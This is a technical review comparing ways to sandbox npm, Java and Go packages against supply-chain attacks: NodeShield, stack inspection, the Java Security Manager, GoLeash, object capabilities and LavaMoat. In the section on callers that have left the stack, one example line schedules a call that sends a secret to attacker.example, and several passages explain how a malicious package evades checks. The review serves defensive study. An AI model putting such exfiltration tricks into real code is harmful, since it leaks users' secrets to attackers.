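| `code` | Running text as code |
| `system` | Reading environment variables and information about the machine |
| `crypto` | Encryption and related functions |

`crypto` gives no access to outside resources. Cornelissen and Balliu included it because attackers use encryption to hide their code and to hold victims' files to ransom.

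NodeShield copies the project and turns each source file in the copy into text that Node.js' `vm` module runs. This module can run code with its own set of global variables, so NodeShield leaves out those the package has no permission for. For example, `fetch` would be undefined in `colour`. NodeShield also replaces every way of importing a module with a version that checks the policy.

Besides permissions, NodeShield enforces the declared dependency tree. It reads the tree from a software bill of materials, a machine-readable list of a program's components and the dependencies between them. A package can import only its own files, its declared dependencies and the built-in modules that its permissions allow.

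The attack on `rate-map` shows why both checks are useful. This small package converts a number between 0 and 1 into a value in another range. It had one dependency and needed no permissions. A malicious version, 1.0.3, located `dl-tar`, which it hadn't declared as a dependency, and used `fs` to overwrite `dl-tar`'s code. This broke the installer for the programming language PureScript, which depended on `rate-map`. NodeShield would have stopped the attack either when `rate-map` looked for `dl-tar` or when it imported `fs`.

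The dependency check helps less if the attacker declares the new dependency. Unlike the system of Ferreira and colleagues, NodeShield lets a package import one that has more permissions than it has itself. An update to `colour` could therefore declare `http-client` as a dependency and send data through it. NodeShield shows reviewers each package's permissions together with those of everything it depends on, so they would see the new permission `network` listed for `colour`, but someone still has to notice and reject the change.

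### What the attack tests measured

Cornelissen and Balliu report that NodeShield could prevent 66 of 67 known attacks. The exception was the attack on `node-ipc`. The legitimate version of that package already used files and the network, so the attacker needed no new permissions. An attacker who compromised `http-client` would have the same advantage.

The 67 malicious versions belonged to 46 packages, 37 of which were malicious from the start. These 37 had no benign version from which to infer a policy, and the permissions that NodeShield inferred from their malicious code often allowed the attack. Cornelissen and Balliu counted such an attack as preventable if removing those permissions would stop it. The result for these packages therefore depends on a developer reviewing the permissions and recognising that they are excessive.

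Only nine of the packages were legitimate ones that had received a malicious update, the kind of attack behind nearly all the download exposure in the Databricks study. NodeShield could stop eight of them, which is encouraging, but the sample is small. Five of the nine attacks ran during installation. The researchers chose those five packages from 1,594 with install-time attacks because earlier studies had covered them. They recommend separate tools for install scripts, which can be written in languages other than JavaScript.

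NodeShield's overhead depends on the type of program. On six web servers, it added about 0.1 milliseconds or less to each request, but it reduced the number of requests they could handle at once by up to 12% and increased memory use by 43% to 251%. NodeShield does most of its work at startup, so it slows short commands more. The documentation tool `dox`, for example, took 235 milliseconds instead of 53.

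When Cornelissen and Balliu repeated the `dox` test using Ferreira and colleagues' method, where each run takes at least five seconds, the slowdown fell from 348% to 3.5%. Ferreira and colleagues' own system may likewise have a noticeable delay at startup, despite the 0.2% slowdown they reported.

Three of 86 packages and programs didn't work with NodeShield. One used an undocumented Node.js function. The other two used `instanceof Array` to test whether a value was a list, which can fail because each set of global variables has its own `Array`. In another test with 24 harmless programs, NodeShield raised false alarms for 4.65% of the accesses it checked, but the test ran only about 15% of the programs' code on average.

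### Code from text, shared objects and arguments

An attacker who can't import `fs` directly might hide the import in text and run it with `eval`. This doesn't work by itself, because the text runs with the same restricted `require` as the code around it. Vasilakis, Staicu and colleagues tested this in *MIR* (2020), an earlier version of their paper, using a library that only passed text to `eval`. Mir inferred two permissions for the library, to use `eval` and to export its function. The researchers then tried more than 800 attacks, but the library could do little beyond arithmetic and simple text operations.

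The greater danger is code that runs in another package's environment or the sandbox's. NodeShield blocks `eval` for packages without the `code` permission. It also moves sensitive functions out of the global object and into local variables, which code running from elsewhere can't reach. Cornelissen and Balliu tried 29 known sandbox escapes on NodeShield, and 27 failed. The other two only changed shared prototypes. Eleven of the 29 worked against Ohm and colleagues' tool.

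Enforcement at run time also catches imports that a search of the source code misses. In 2018, attackers added the package `flatmap-stream` to the dependencies of `event-stream` to steal from users of Copay, a cryptocurrency wallet. The package's main code was encrypted, so NodeShield's source analysis assigned it only the `system` permission. When the package ran, it tried to use encryption, files and the network, and NodeShield blocked it.

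Shared objects are a weaker point, because a package can change a built-in method that other packages rely on. For example, it could make the function that checks whether a list contains an item always return true. If NodeShield used that function to check its list of permitted imports, every import would pass, so NodeShield saves the original functions before any package runs. But it doesn't protect packages from each other in this way, so `colour` might be able to alter a shared object that `http-client` uses and influence what it sends.

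Cornelissen and Balliu left this gap deliberately, because benign packages also change built-in objects, for instance to add features missing from older runtimes. Ferreira and colleagues closed it by requiring the `all` permission for such changes, so more than half of npm packages needed it. Neither choice is satisfactory. A program's developers can freeze the built-in objects if none of its packages needs to change them.

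Import checks also don't cover what a package receives as an argument. `colour` takes only text, so it gains nothing this way. But if the server passes `logger` a visitor's whole request object so that it can record the address, that object may also contain the visitor's password and an open network connection, which `logger` could use without importing anything. Ferreira and colleagues allow this and make the caller responsible for what it passes. They think an attacker's package is unlikely to receive exactly the object it needs. Mir doesn't check arguments either, and Cornelissen and Balliu treat anything passed to a package as entrusted to it and its dependencies.

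### Passing tokens to built-in functions

Joseph Gentle, in *NodeJS packages don't deserve your trust*, proposes to make passed references the basis of the system. Under his scheme, any package could import `fs`, but its functions would work only if the caller supplied a token for the operation. The program's main package would start with a token that allows everything, and could derive narrower ones to hand out. The web server might do this for `logger`:

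```js
const logToken = cap.narrow(rootToken, { fs: { write: "./logs" } });
logger.start({ token: logToken });
```

Attenuation means deriving a weaker right from a stronger one. A package can narrow its token further before passing it on, but can never widen it. With attenuation, `logger` gets access to only one folder, whereas NodeShield's `file-system` permission covers the whole disk. `colour` receives no token, so it can import `fs` but can't use it to read a file.

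Gentle's proposal is a sketch, and he points out several unsolved problems. ES modules run all imported files before the first line of the main file, so if the main package has to call a function to claim the unlimited token, an imported package could claim it first. He suggests that Node.js could hand the token directly to the main package. He also worries that packages could tamper with built-in objects to steal tokens, and would be happy to ban `eval` and some other dynamic features to prevent it. The system would be optional, so existing programs would keep working with the flag off.

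With the flag on, every package that opens files or connections would have to accept a token and pass it along. For packages that nobody updates, Gentle suggests a `bless` function that would assign a token to a package by name. Node.js would then have to work out whether a call to `fs` came from that package, probably by looking at the chain of function calls that led to it. He notes that JavaScript code can already inspect this chain, but that this is slow and the result could probably be manipulated.

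## Limiting a package by checking the call stack

Gentle's `bless` function would have Node.js examine the chain of function calls behind each call to `fs`. Java used this technique, called stack inspection, for more than two decades. The runtime checks permissions when code tries to open a file or a connection, rather than when the code imports a module.

A running program keeps a call stack, a list of the functions that have started but not yet returned. When the web server calls `colour`, and `colour` calls `http-client`, functions from all three are on the stack. If `http-client` then tries to open a connection, the runtime works out which package each function belongs to, and allows the connection only if every one of those packages has permission for it. If P(x) is the set of permissions of package x, the code can do only what is in the intersection:

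```
allowed = P(server) ∩ P(colour) ∩ P(http-client)
```

Suppose the policy lets the server use the network and write to `./logs`, lets `http-client` use the network, lets `logger` write to `./logs`, and gives `colour` no permissions.

| Packages on the stack | Intersection |
|---|---|
| server → `http-client` | network |
| server → `logger` | write to `./logs` |
| server → `colour` → `http-client` | nothing |

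The server can fetch a page through `http-client`, but `colour` can't use it to send a stolen token. The restriction applies both when `colour` loads and when the server later calls it, because its code is on the stack each time. Install scripts still need a separate limit.

Ferreira and colleagues' import rule would stop `colour` from loading `http-client`. Stack inspection would let `colour` load `http-client` and use a function that only assembles web addresses. The runtime would intervene only if a call reached the network.

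### The confused deputy

A simpler check would look only at the package that makes the request directly. When `colour` calls `http-client`, the check would pass because `http-client` is allowed to use the network. `http-client` would then be a confused deputy, a component tricked into using its legitimate access for code that lacks it.

The intersection prevents this because adding a package to the stack can only shrink the set of allowed operations. `colour` therefore gains no permissions by calling a more powerful package or by being called by one, for instance if `http-client` uses `colour` to format an error message.

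The drawback is that every caller needs the permissions of the packages it calls. If `http-client` starts keeping a cache on disk, the server and any package between it and `http-client` also need permission to write to the cache folder, even if their own code never touches it.

### Code that vouches for its caller

A strict intersection also blocks harmless operations. In *JEP 486*, a proposal for changing Java, Mullan and Buckley (2024) give the example of a program that requests the local time but has no permission to read files. Java's time library has to read a time-zone file to provide the time, and the check would fail because the program is on the stack.

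Java's solution was a method called `doPrivileged`, which lets code use a permission that its callers lack. The runtime checks the stack from the newest function backwards and stops at the function that called `doPrivileged`. That function's package still needs the permission, but the packages that called it do not. The time library can therefore read its file for any program.

A library can safely use `doPrivileged` only if its caller can't misuse the operation. For example, a program that calls a library to get the time can't choose which file the library reads. But if `http-client` used `doPrivileged` for requests to any address it received, `colour` could again use `http-client` to send the token, which would make it a confused deputy. Each use of `doPrivileged` moves a security decision from the policy into the library's code, so the library's author has to get it right.

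### Callers that have left the stack

The stack contains only functions that haven't returned, so `colour` can avoid the check by arranging for a call to happen later:

```js
setTimeout(httpClient.get, 0, "https://attacker.example/?t=" + secret);
```

This schedules `httpClient.get` to run as soon as the current work finishes. By then `colour` has returned, so `http-client` is the only package on the stack. If `colour` instead passed the timer its own function that called `httpClient.get`, code from `colour` would be on the stack again and the check would fail. Callbacks are therefore a problem mainly when one package schedules another package's function directly.

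A runtime can fix this by storing the caller's permissions with each scheduled task and including them in the later check. This is easiest when one thread creates another, because the new thread can inherit a record of its parent's stack. It is harder when a package puts a request in a queue and an existing thread picks it up, because the runtime would have to attach the permissions to the request.

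A stack check also misses packages that influence a call through shared data. Suppose `http-client` keeps its default settings in an object that other packages can change. `colour` sets the attacker's machine as the proxy, the intermediary through which requests pass, and returns. When the server next fetches a page, the stack contains the server and `http-client`, which are both allowed to use the network, so the check passes and the request goes to the attacker.

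A rule that limited `http-client` to `api.example.com` would stop this attack, though `colour` might still be able to alter what the server sends there. The runtime could also record every package that has run so far and include them all in the intersection, but then the server would lose all its permissions the first time it coloured a line of text.

### Java's Security Manager

Java's version of these checks was called the Security Manager. *JEP 411* (2021), by OpenJDK, the project that develops Java, traces its history. The first version of Java included it to protect people's computers from applets, small programs that web browsers downloaded and ran. It let local code do anything but kept applets away from files and the network.

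Java 1.2 replaced this division with least privilege. All code was now untrusted by default, and a policy file granted permissions to code according to where it came from, such as a particular JAR, the archive in which Java libraries are distributed. A rule for `logger` could look like this:

```
grant codeBase "file:/app/lib/logger.jar" {
  permission java.io.FilePermission "/app/logs/-", "write";
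};
```

Without such a rule for `colour.jar`, a malicious `colour` couldn't have read the token or connected to the attacker's server. Java had per-library permissions long before npm existed, but hardly anyone used them. The Security Manager was off by default for programs started from the command line, and only a handful of applications, such as the search engine Elasticsearch, came with policies for their own code.

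OpenJDK gives three reasons for this. First, developers had to list every permission a program needed, even if they only wanted to limit which files it could read, because the policy language couldn't express "everything except". Second, applications needed the permissions of all the libraries they called, and few library authors were willing to learn how to use `doPrivileged` safely. It was easier to grant a JAR `AllPermission`, which removed the protection. Third, the checks were often too slow.

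Maintaining the Security Manager also took a lot of work. Mullan and Buckley count over 1,000 methods in Java's own libraries that had to check permissions and over 1,200 that had to elevate privileges so that their callers would pass these checks. The maintainers had to review every change to these methods with the permission system in mind. About 4,000 tests covered the Security Manager, and removing it meant deleting more than 50,000 lines of code.

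Java 17 marked the Security Manager for removal in 2021, and Java 24 disabled it permanently. Its classes remain for compatibility, but Java exits with an error if someone tries to enable it at startup.

Some developers objected. The campaign site *Discuss JEP 411* pointed out that most applications don't need everything Java can do, such as compiling and running new code, and that the Security Manager let developers take away the rest with a configuration file. The proposal offered no replacement. Firmstone's *Why JEP 411 Will Have a Negative Impact on Java Security* also argued from least privilege. According to Apache's *Better JEP 411 News*, the maintainers agreed in May 2021 to let programs keep installing their own Security Manager in Java 17, with a warning, and postponed blocking this by default until Java 18.

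The maintainers' argument that few people used the Security Manager seems strong. Mullan and Buckley saw hardly any discussion of the warnings after Java 17 came out, and say that most of the few applications that enabled the Security Manager granted all permissions to all their code. The maintainers' argument about threats is weaker. OpenJDK argues that malicious remote code is less of a danger because Java no longer runs applets, and treats local code mainly as a source of accidental security holes. A hijacked library doesn't fit this division because it is malicious remote code that the developer's own tools install locally. The recommended alternatives, such as containers and operating system sandboxes, limit whole programs, so they can't give `colour` fewer permissions than the server.

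### ZTD-Java

*ZTDJAVA* (Amusuo, Robinson and colleagues, 2023) presents ZTD-Java, which tries to keep the per-library permissions without the Security Manager's main drawbacks. It changes Java's own classes as they load, adding a check to just four operations: opening a file to read, opening a file to write, connecting to another machine and starting a program. By comparison, the Security Manager protected more than 100 methods with 28 kinds of permission.

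Distinguishing direct permissions from transitive ones reduces the spread of permissions to callers. A direct permission lets a package perform an operation itself, while a transitive permission only lets it do so through another package that has the direct one. For example, a `weather` package that downloads forecasts through `http-client` needs only transitive permission to contact the forecast server. If that is all it is granted, it can't open a connection on its own.

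ZTD-Java generates the policy from a record of what the program does as it runs. When a package performs one of the four operations, it gets a direct permission, and the other packages on the stack get transitive ones. In 16 test applications, this produced an average of two or three permissions for each package that needed any, and most applications had fewer than ten such packages. The policies are short partly because programs use only a small part of what their libraries can do. In nine applications with a total of 103 dependencies, 46 dependencies contained code that could read files, but only four read any during the tests. Fifteen contained code that could start other programs, but none did so during the tests.

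Amusuo and colleagues recreated 15 known vulnerabilities in small programs, and ZTD-Java blocked all the attacks on them. It also blocked nine of these when the researchers added the vulnerable libraries to real applications. But these vulnerabilities were accidental, like the 2021 one in the logging library Log4j, so the results are only indirect evidence of how well ZTD-Java would block malicious updates.

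The average slowdown was close to zero, against 21% for the Security Manager. Most of that 21% comes from one program, the code editor Eclipse, which took three times as long. Running time changed by less than 1% for eight of the 12 applications that ran under the Security Manager. This suggests that the slowness OpenJDK complains about depended heavily on the program. Four more applications failed to run under the Security Manager, which may have been the bigger problem.

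ZTD-Java reduces overhead partly by checking less. A developer would have to add Java's other ways to open a file, such as the `RandomAccessFile` class, to the list. ZTD-Java also identifies packages by the beginning of their class names, so a malicious package could choose names that make it look like part of `http-client`. Leaving a package out of the policy may also be unsafe. According to the notes on Amusuo and colleagues' algorithm, a package without defined permissions passes the check if its caller does, although they describe the default as no trust. `colour` should therefore have an explicit entry that denies it everything.

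Checking the call stack misses callers that have already left it. In ZTD-Java, a new thread inherits its parent's policies, but those policies don't follow requests passed between independent threads. Amusuo and colleagues mention two possible remedies, which are taint tracking, with the high overhead described in the previous section, and requiring permission to communicate with other threads.

### Deno's `--deny-module` prototype

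Around May 2026, a Deno developer wrote a change that would bring stack inspection to JavaScript packages. The commit message, *feat(permissions): add --deny-module for per-module permission restrictions*, includes this example:

```
deno run --deny-module=npm:chalk:all main.ts
```

`chalk` is a real package that colours terminal text, much like `colour`. With this flag, Deno would refuse any operation that needs a permission while code from `chalk` is anywhere on the stack, even if the program as a whole has that permission. A rule can also name particular permissions, such as `net,run`. Patterns that start with `npm:` or `jsr:` (Deno's own registry) match a package by name. Deno looks for any other pattern as plain text in the address of each file on the stack.

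The flag can only deny. If D(x) is the set of permissions denied to package x, the result for a stack with two packages is:

```
allowed = P(program) − (D(package 1) ∪ D(package 2))
```

This is the same as an intersection in which every package starts with all the program's permissions and loses the ones listed in its rule. It avoids the Security Manager's all-or-nothing policies, because a developer can restrict one package without restricting the others. But a package without a rule keeps all of its permissions, even if it is a transitive dependency added in a later update. The rules also cover whole categories of access, so they could block `http-client` from the network but not limit it to one host.

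Recording the stack is slow, so the prototype would do it only if the developer has set at least one rule. Other programs would not be slowed down. The commit message includes no figures for the slowdown in programs with rules.

There is no evidence that Deno merged or released the flag. The Deno 2.9 release notes don't mention it, although they don't list every change, and Deno's documentation still rules out different privilege levels within a thread. A second Deno prototype from about July, *feat(permissions): prototype per-API (capability) permissions*, would instead apply to the whole program, letting a developer allow `fetch` but not other ways of using the network.

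An official release now looks unlikely. Willison (2026) reports in *Deno is joining Cloudflare* that the internet infrastructure company Cloudflare acquired Deno on 9 October 2026. Deno's team plans one more year of bug fixes and security updates, and will then stop developing the runtime. The code remains open source, so others could still finish the feature.

### Attributing system calls to Go packages

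The compiler for the Go language combines a program and all its packages into one file of machine code, and Go has no built-in counterpart to the Security Manager. GoLeash (Cesarano, Monperrus and Natella, 2025) therefore monitors system calls, the requests a program makes to the operating system.

GoLeash uses eBPF, a Linux feature that runs small monitoring programs inside the kernel. For each system call, eBPF records the kind of call and the monitored program's call stack. A separate program translates the memory addresses on the stack into function and package names. It skips Go's standard library and attributes the system call to the most recent function from another package. It then assigns the system call to one of a few categories, such as reading files or connecting to another machine.

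To build a policy, the developer runs the program's tests while GoLeash records which categories each package uses and which sequences of packages led to each use. In production, GoLeash reports a violation if either the category or the sequence is new. This can be stricter than intersecting the packages' permissions. For example, if the server never reached the network through `weather` and then `http-client` during the tests, GoLeash would flag that route even if all three packages have network permission. It therefore catches a confused deputy without requiring callers to hold the permissions of the packages they call.

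Cesarano and colleagues tested GoLeash on five large programs, including Kubernetes, which manages software across many machines. They inserted five kinds of malicious behaviour, modelled on real attacks in other languages, one at a time into each of the 653 packages that ran during normal use. GoLeash detected 98% on average, compared with 32% for a policy that covered the whole program. The 32% was partly luck, because the two behaviours that the broader policy caught happened to use a rare system call that the original programs didn't need.

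GoLeash missed attacks when the compromised package already had the permissions they required. It checks the category of an operation but not its target, so a compromised `http-client` could send data to a new host along its usual route. Hiding the malicious code made little difference to detection on average, though in one program detection of data theft fell to 77% when the malicious code was written in C.

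The monitoring added between 1.3% and 5.1% to the processor time for each request. Tracking only the whole program added 0.2% to 1.6%, so most of the overhead comes from working out which package is responsible.

Cesarano and colleagues saw no false alarms during the performance tests, but they used the same workloads to create and enforce the policies, which makes false alarms almost impossible. A real program would eventually do something its tests didn't cover. As with Mir, the packages also have to be free of malicious code when the developer creates the policy. A fake version of the Go database package BoltDB stayed available for years and contacted its attacker's server whenever it ran. GoLeash would have allowed that connection unless a developer reviewing the policy questioned why a local database needed the network.

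GoLeash can log a violation or end the program, but it seems the first forbidden call could finish before that happens, because the kernel passes its records on without waiting for an answer. One call may be enough to send a short token. GoLeash also relies on the stack being genuine, but C code inside the program shares its memory and could in principle forge the list of callers. Go code can also easily hide a caller without forging anything. The `go` keyword starts a function concurrently on a new stack, so `colour` could use it to start a function from `http-client` and leave no trace of itself on that stack. The attack would then succeed if `http-client` normally made connections from a stack of its own.

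## Object capabilities: access only to what code is handed

A stack check has to identify the packages behind each request, and `colour` can escape it by returning before the request happens. The object-capability model makes this identification unnecessary. A package can use only the objects it has references to, and it starts with none that lead to files, the network or secrets. If no other code hands `colour` a way to reach the network, `colour` can't reach it, regardless of when its code runs or what is on the stack.

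Dennis and Van Horn defined capabilities in *Programming Semantics for Multiprogrammed Computations* (1966), an article about computers that run programs for several users at once. In their design, the operating system keeps a list of capabilities for each computation. Each capability points to an object, such as a segment of memory, and records what the computation may do with it, for instance read it but not change it. A program uses a capability by giving its position in the list, and can't make one up because it can change the list only through the operating system.

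By 1973, several researchers had noticed that object-oriented languages already contain something similar, namely the references that objects hold to one another. Miller (2006), in *Robust Composition*, worked this out as a full security model. An object can get a reference to another object in only four ways:

- It had the reference when the program started.
- It created the other object.
- Its own creator had the reference and built it in.
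- A third object that had references to both of them passed it on.

Two groups of objects with no references between them can therefore never become connected. If the server is the only link between them, only the server can give one group a reference to the other.

Most languages don't follow these rules. C++ code can forge a reference by turning a number into a pointer. Other languages have what Miller calls magic names, which give any code that uses them access to something powerful. In Node.js, `"fs"` is a magic name, so the server can't withhold file access from a package that uses it.

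*Objects as Secure Capabilities* (Duffy, 2015) describes Midori, an operating system built on this model. Duffy notes that a capability is just an object, so programmers can make it as broad or as narrow as they like. He warns that the "capabilities" of Linux and Android are something else. One of them, a flag called `CAP_CHOWN`, lets a process change the owner of any file on the machine. *Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) points out that the set of these flags is fixed, so a program can't create a new one for a single file.

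### One file for `logger`

With capabilities, the web server could set up its log like this:

```js
function makeAppender(path) {
  const file = fs.openSync(path, "a");   // "a": append only
  function append(line) {
    fs.writeSync(file, `${line}\n`);
  }
  return harden({ append });
}

logger.start(makeAppender("./logs/server.log"));
logger.info(colour.green("Server started"));
```

`logger` receives an object with one method, `append`, which lets it add lines to one file in `./logs` but not read the file, change earlier lines or open another file. Because `logger` never supplies a path, it can't use the links and alternative spellings that bypassed some of Deno's rules. The `harden` function, from a restricted form of JavaScript called Hardened JavaScript, makes the object and everything reachable from it unchangeable, so that one package can't replace `append` for the others.

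`colour` receives text and returns text. The attacker's update can't read the publishing token or contact the attacker's server, because it has no reference to an object that does either. It can still return false text, which the server passes to `logger`. Miller calls this indirect influence authority, as opposed to direct access. `colour` has some authority over the contents of the log file even though it can't access the file. No access rule can remove that authority while the server keeps using the text `colour` returns.

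### Attenuation, revocation and membranes

`makeAppender` is an example of attenuation, because it derives access to one file from access to the whole disk. `logger` can attenuate further, for example by wrapping its object in another that accepts at most 100 lines and giving that to a dependency that formats error reports. A permission system would need a new kind of rule for such a limit, but here it takes a counter and an `if` statement. In the 2026 lecture *Designing “least-authority” JavaScript apps*, Van Cutsem splits a log into a `reader` and a `writer` object that share the same messages, so the program can hand each package only the one it needs.

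Taking access back looks harder, because nobody can remove a reference from the code that holds it. Some researchers concluded that capability systems can't revoke access at all. Miller, Yee and Shapiro reply that Redell had published a solution in 1974. Instead of the real object, the server hands over a forwarding object that it can switch off:

```js
function makeRevocable(target) {
  const forwarder = {
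    append(line) { target.append(line); }
  };
  function revoke() { target = null; }
  return harden([forwarder, revoke]);
}
```

After the server calls `revoke`, the package still has the forwarder, but every call to it fails. If the package has passed the forwarder to other code, that code loses access too. Revocation can't undo the package's earlier writes or take back data it has already read.

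The server can use the same function to limit a single call. Suppose `http-client` has a function `download` that saves a page to a file:

```js
const [output, revoke] = makeRevocable(makeAppender("./reports/today.csv"));
try {
  await httpClient.download(reportUrl, output);
} finally {
  revoke();
}
```

`download` can write to this file until it finishes, while `http-client`'s other functions receive no file. This per-function limit needs no policy file because the call shows what the function gets. Functions in the same package can share variables, so if access weren't revoked at the end, `download` could store `output` and any other function in `http-client` could use it later.

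A simple forwarder can't fully revoke access if the object behind it returns other objects. For example, the server might give a package a revocable folder object whose `open` method returns files. After the server revokes the folder, the package can't open more files, but those it has already opened keep working. A membrane prevents this by also wrapping every object that a call returns or receives as an argument. Numbers and text pass through unwrapped. A single switch disables all the wrappers.

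Putting a membrane around only one or two risky components limits the slowdown and compatibility problems that led Ferreira and colleagues to reject membranes for all of npm. Van Cutsem reports that Firefox uses membranes to separate websites from the browser's privileged JavaScript.

### What JavaScript needs

JavaScript already meets two of the conditions. Code can't forge a reference, and a function can hide an object in a local variable, as `makeAppender` does with `file`. But all packages in a program share built-in objects that any of them can change, and every package starts with access to powerful modules and global objects.

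Hardened JavaScript changes both. A program first calls `lockdown()`, which freezes the built-in objects. After that, `colour` can't replace `Array.prototype.push`, the method that adds an item to any list in the program. The program then creates compartments, separate environments for running code. Each has its own global object, and whoever creates the compartment decides what that object contains and which modules the code may import. In a compartment for `colour`, `fetch` and `process` wouldn't exist, and importing `fs` would fail. Any text that `colour` runs as code with `eval` stays in the same compartment.

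The documentation in npm's *Secure EcmaScript (SES)* shows which parts the compartments share:

```js
const box = new Compartment();
box.globalThis === globalThis;   // false: its own global object
box.globalThis.Array === Array;  // true: the same frozen built-in
```

Compartments share one `Array`, which is safe because it is frozen. Sharing it avoids the problem with `instanceof Array` that broke two programs under NodeShield.

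Freezing causes a different problem, because it can break packages that add to the built-in objects. Judging by Ferreira and colleagues' figures, about a fifth of npm packages did so in 2018 (21.9% needed the `all` permission for their own code, nearly always for this reason). The share that would break is probably lower, because that estimate was somewhat pessimistic and some packages add features only if the runtime lacks them. After the freeze, `colour` couldn't add `green` to strings, but `colour.green("text")` would work.

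Compartments also fail to prevent some attacks. Code in a compartment runs on the same thread as the rest of the program, so `colour` can stop the server with an endless loop. Miller's model covers only ordinary communication between objects, not covert channels, in which code leaks information through side effects such as how long a calculation takes.

### Endo and the JavaScript standard

Van Cutsem traces Hardened JavaScript to Caja, a Google project from about 2009 for embedding other people's scripts safely in web pages. Its developers later tried to add its main features to the JavaScript standard under the name Secure ECMAScript, or SES. That effort stalled, but work continued in the open-source project Endo. The company Agoric renamed SES "Hardened JavaScript" around 2020.

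Endo maintains the npm package `ses`, which adds `lockdown`, `harden` and `Compartment` to ordinary JavaScript engines. Endo also has a loader that reads each package's declared dependencies and puts each package in its own compartment. The program's developer can then pass powerful objects to the packages that need them. Endo can therefore sandbox libraries today without changes to Node.js or browsers.

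TC39, the committee behind the JavaScript standard, moves proposals through numbered stages up to Stage 4, when they are ready for the standard. TC39's *Compartments* is still at Stage 1, where the committee has agreed only to explore the idea. Its supporters have since split it up. According to a reply in the forum thread *What is the current status of SES, tinySES and Jessie?*, they took the part about loading modules to a TC39 group called Modules Harmony. The part about running code with a different global object became a separate proposal, Endo's *new Global*, which in August 2025 had not yet been presented for Stage 1. A TC39 meeting agenda lists *new Global* with a proposal that would let a program control what code imports, which a library sandbox also needs.

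ShadowRealm is further along, at Stage 2.7 in TC39's *ShadowRealm API* (2025). It creates an environment with its own complete set of built-in objects, and code outside can call functions inside through wrappers. The forum reply describes it as useful but separate from Hardened JavaScript. Separate built-ins would stop `colour` from tampering with other packages' objects, but they would bring back the problem with `instanceof Array`.

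In 2026, as Van Cutsem notes, JavaScript still has no standard way to isolate a module. XS, an engine for small devices, has built-in support for most of the Compartments proposal, according to Moddable's *XS Compartment* (2022). On other engines, developers depend on the `ses` package, which has to run before any untrusted code. Its maintainers have to account for every new built-in object that engines add.

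### LavaMoat for existing packages

Almost no npm package expects its caller to hand it a file or a connection. The existing `logger` simply imports `fs`, and would fail in an empty compartment. LavaMoat, a set of tools from the makers of the cryptocurrency wallet MetaMask, makes such packages work by using a policy file. It runs each package in its own compartment and adds only the global objects and modules that the policy lists for it:

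```json
{
  "resources": {
    "logger": {
      "builtin": { "fs.appendFile": true }
    },
    "http-client": {
      "builtin": { "https": true },
      "packages": { "http-client>url-tools": true }
    }
  }
}
```

`colour` has no entry, so it gets no built-in modules or global objects such as `fetch`. The name `http-client>url-tools` identifies `url-tools` as a transitive dependency reached through `http-client`. LavaMoat can automatically generate a policy from the packages' code as a starting point for developers.

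The `packages` list closes a gap that NodeShield leaves open. If an update to `colour` declares `http-client` as a new dependency, the import fails until someone adds `http-client` to the policy, so `colour` cannot use it as a confused deputy just by declaring it.

LavaMoat restricts access less precisely than a program written with capabilities. This policy lets `logger` append to any file the user can change, whereas `makeAppender` restricts it to one. The policy also doesn't limit which machines `http-client` may contact. Developers can combine the two approaches, using LavaMoat to keep old packages away from powerful modules and passing objects that give only narrow access in the code they write themselves.

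For installation, LavaMoat has a separate tool called `allow-scripts`, which turns off install scripts except for packages the developer has approved.

*Widespread npm Supply Chain Attack* (2025), by the cloud security company Wiz, describes an attack on `chalk`, the real package that resembles `colour`. On 8 September 2025, an attacker tricked a well-known developer into giving up control of his npm account, and published malicious versions of `chalk`, `debug` and other packages. The malicious versions were available for only about two hours, but Wiz estimates that the malware was present in about 10% of the environments in its data. In web pages, the malware replaced `fetch` with its own version and swapped cryptocurrency addresses for the attacker's.

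In *How to survive supply-chain attacks*, Obici tested this malware against LavaMoat, using a policy generated from `chalk` 5.6.0, the last clean version. The policy allowed the package to read two properties describing the browser and nothing else. The malicious version 5.6.1 crashed when it tried to replace `fetch`, because it couldn't change the global object.

This demonstration is convincing, but it covers only one package and came after the attack was known. The attack was also an easy case for LavaMoat, since a package that colours text needs almost no access. Obici's company, OtterSec, had audited LavaMoat's plugin for the build tool Webpack in late 2024 and found vulnerabilities that let attackers bypass the protection. He also warns that developers who regenerate the policy while a malicious version is installed may approve whatever access the malware needs.

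Some of the 2026 attacks look equally easy to contain. `@asyncapi/specs` contains descriptions of a data format and has no obvious need to start a program, so a policy based on a clean version should have stopped the attack's first step, but only for people who ran the affected tools under LavaMoat. `ordered-btree` was malicious from the start, so, as with NodeShield, a generated policy might have allowed the attack unless a reviewer objected.

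MetaMask uses LavaMoat to sandbox plugins in its wallet, according to Van Cutsem. Accepting some inconvenience for security makes sense in a wallet, because malicious code can steal money within seconds. Existing apps don't need a rewrite, according to LavaMoat's README, but it has no measurements of slowdown or of how many packages work unchanged. NodeShield's figures are a poor substitute because, although both tools do extra work at startup, they isolate packages differently. A team considering LavaMoat should therefore measure slowdown and compatibility on its own program.

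### Rewriting libraries and passing references around

LavaMoat lets developers postpone rewriting libraries, but a program gets the full precision of capabilities only if its libraries accept objects instead of importing modules. Packages that need no permissions, nearly a third of npm by Ferreira and colleagues' estimate, could mostly stay as they are. The rest include old packages that nobody maintains. A developer can put a small wrapper around such a package or leave it under LavaMoat, so libraries can be converted gradually.

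Critics also worry about long chains of parameters. If the server calls `weather`, and `weather` calls `http-client`, each function along the way would need an extra parameter for the network connection. Programs can avoid much of this by passing references when they create objects:

```js
const client = makeHttpClient(connectTo("api.example.com"));
const weather = makeWeather(client);

weather.forecast("Oslo");
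```

Any code that has `weather` can now request a forecast without its own network connection. `makeWeather` has a responsibility similar to that of a Java library that uses `doPrivileged`, but the worst it can do with `client` is misuse a connection to one machine.

When a package deep in the program needs access to something new, every constructor in the chain leading to it has to change. This is real work for a team that updates hundreds of packages a year. It is also partly an advantage for security, because a bug-fix release of `colour` can't start using the network unless someone changes the code that creates or calls it.

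### Leaked references and audits

The safety of a capability depends on the code that holds it, and Van Cutsem's lecture shows how easily a careful-looking program can leak one. His first version of a message log is a class of a few lines whose `read()` method returns the log's own list of messages instead of a copy. A package that should only read the messages can therefore delete them all by setting the list's length to 0. Freezing the log object doesn't prevent this, because the list inside it has to stay changeable.

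Wallach and colleagues raised this objection more generally in a paper on Java security. They argued that any code that receives a capability "must be trusted to care for it properly", and that a system running downloaded code has too many such recipients. Miller, Yee and Shapiro reply that code can pass a reference only to objects it can reach. If `logger` has no connection to an untrusted package, it can't give that package its file, even deliberately.

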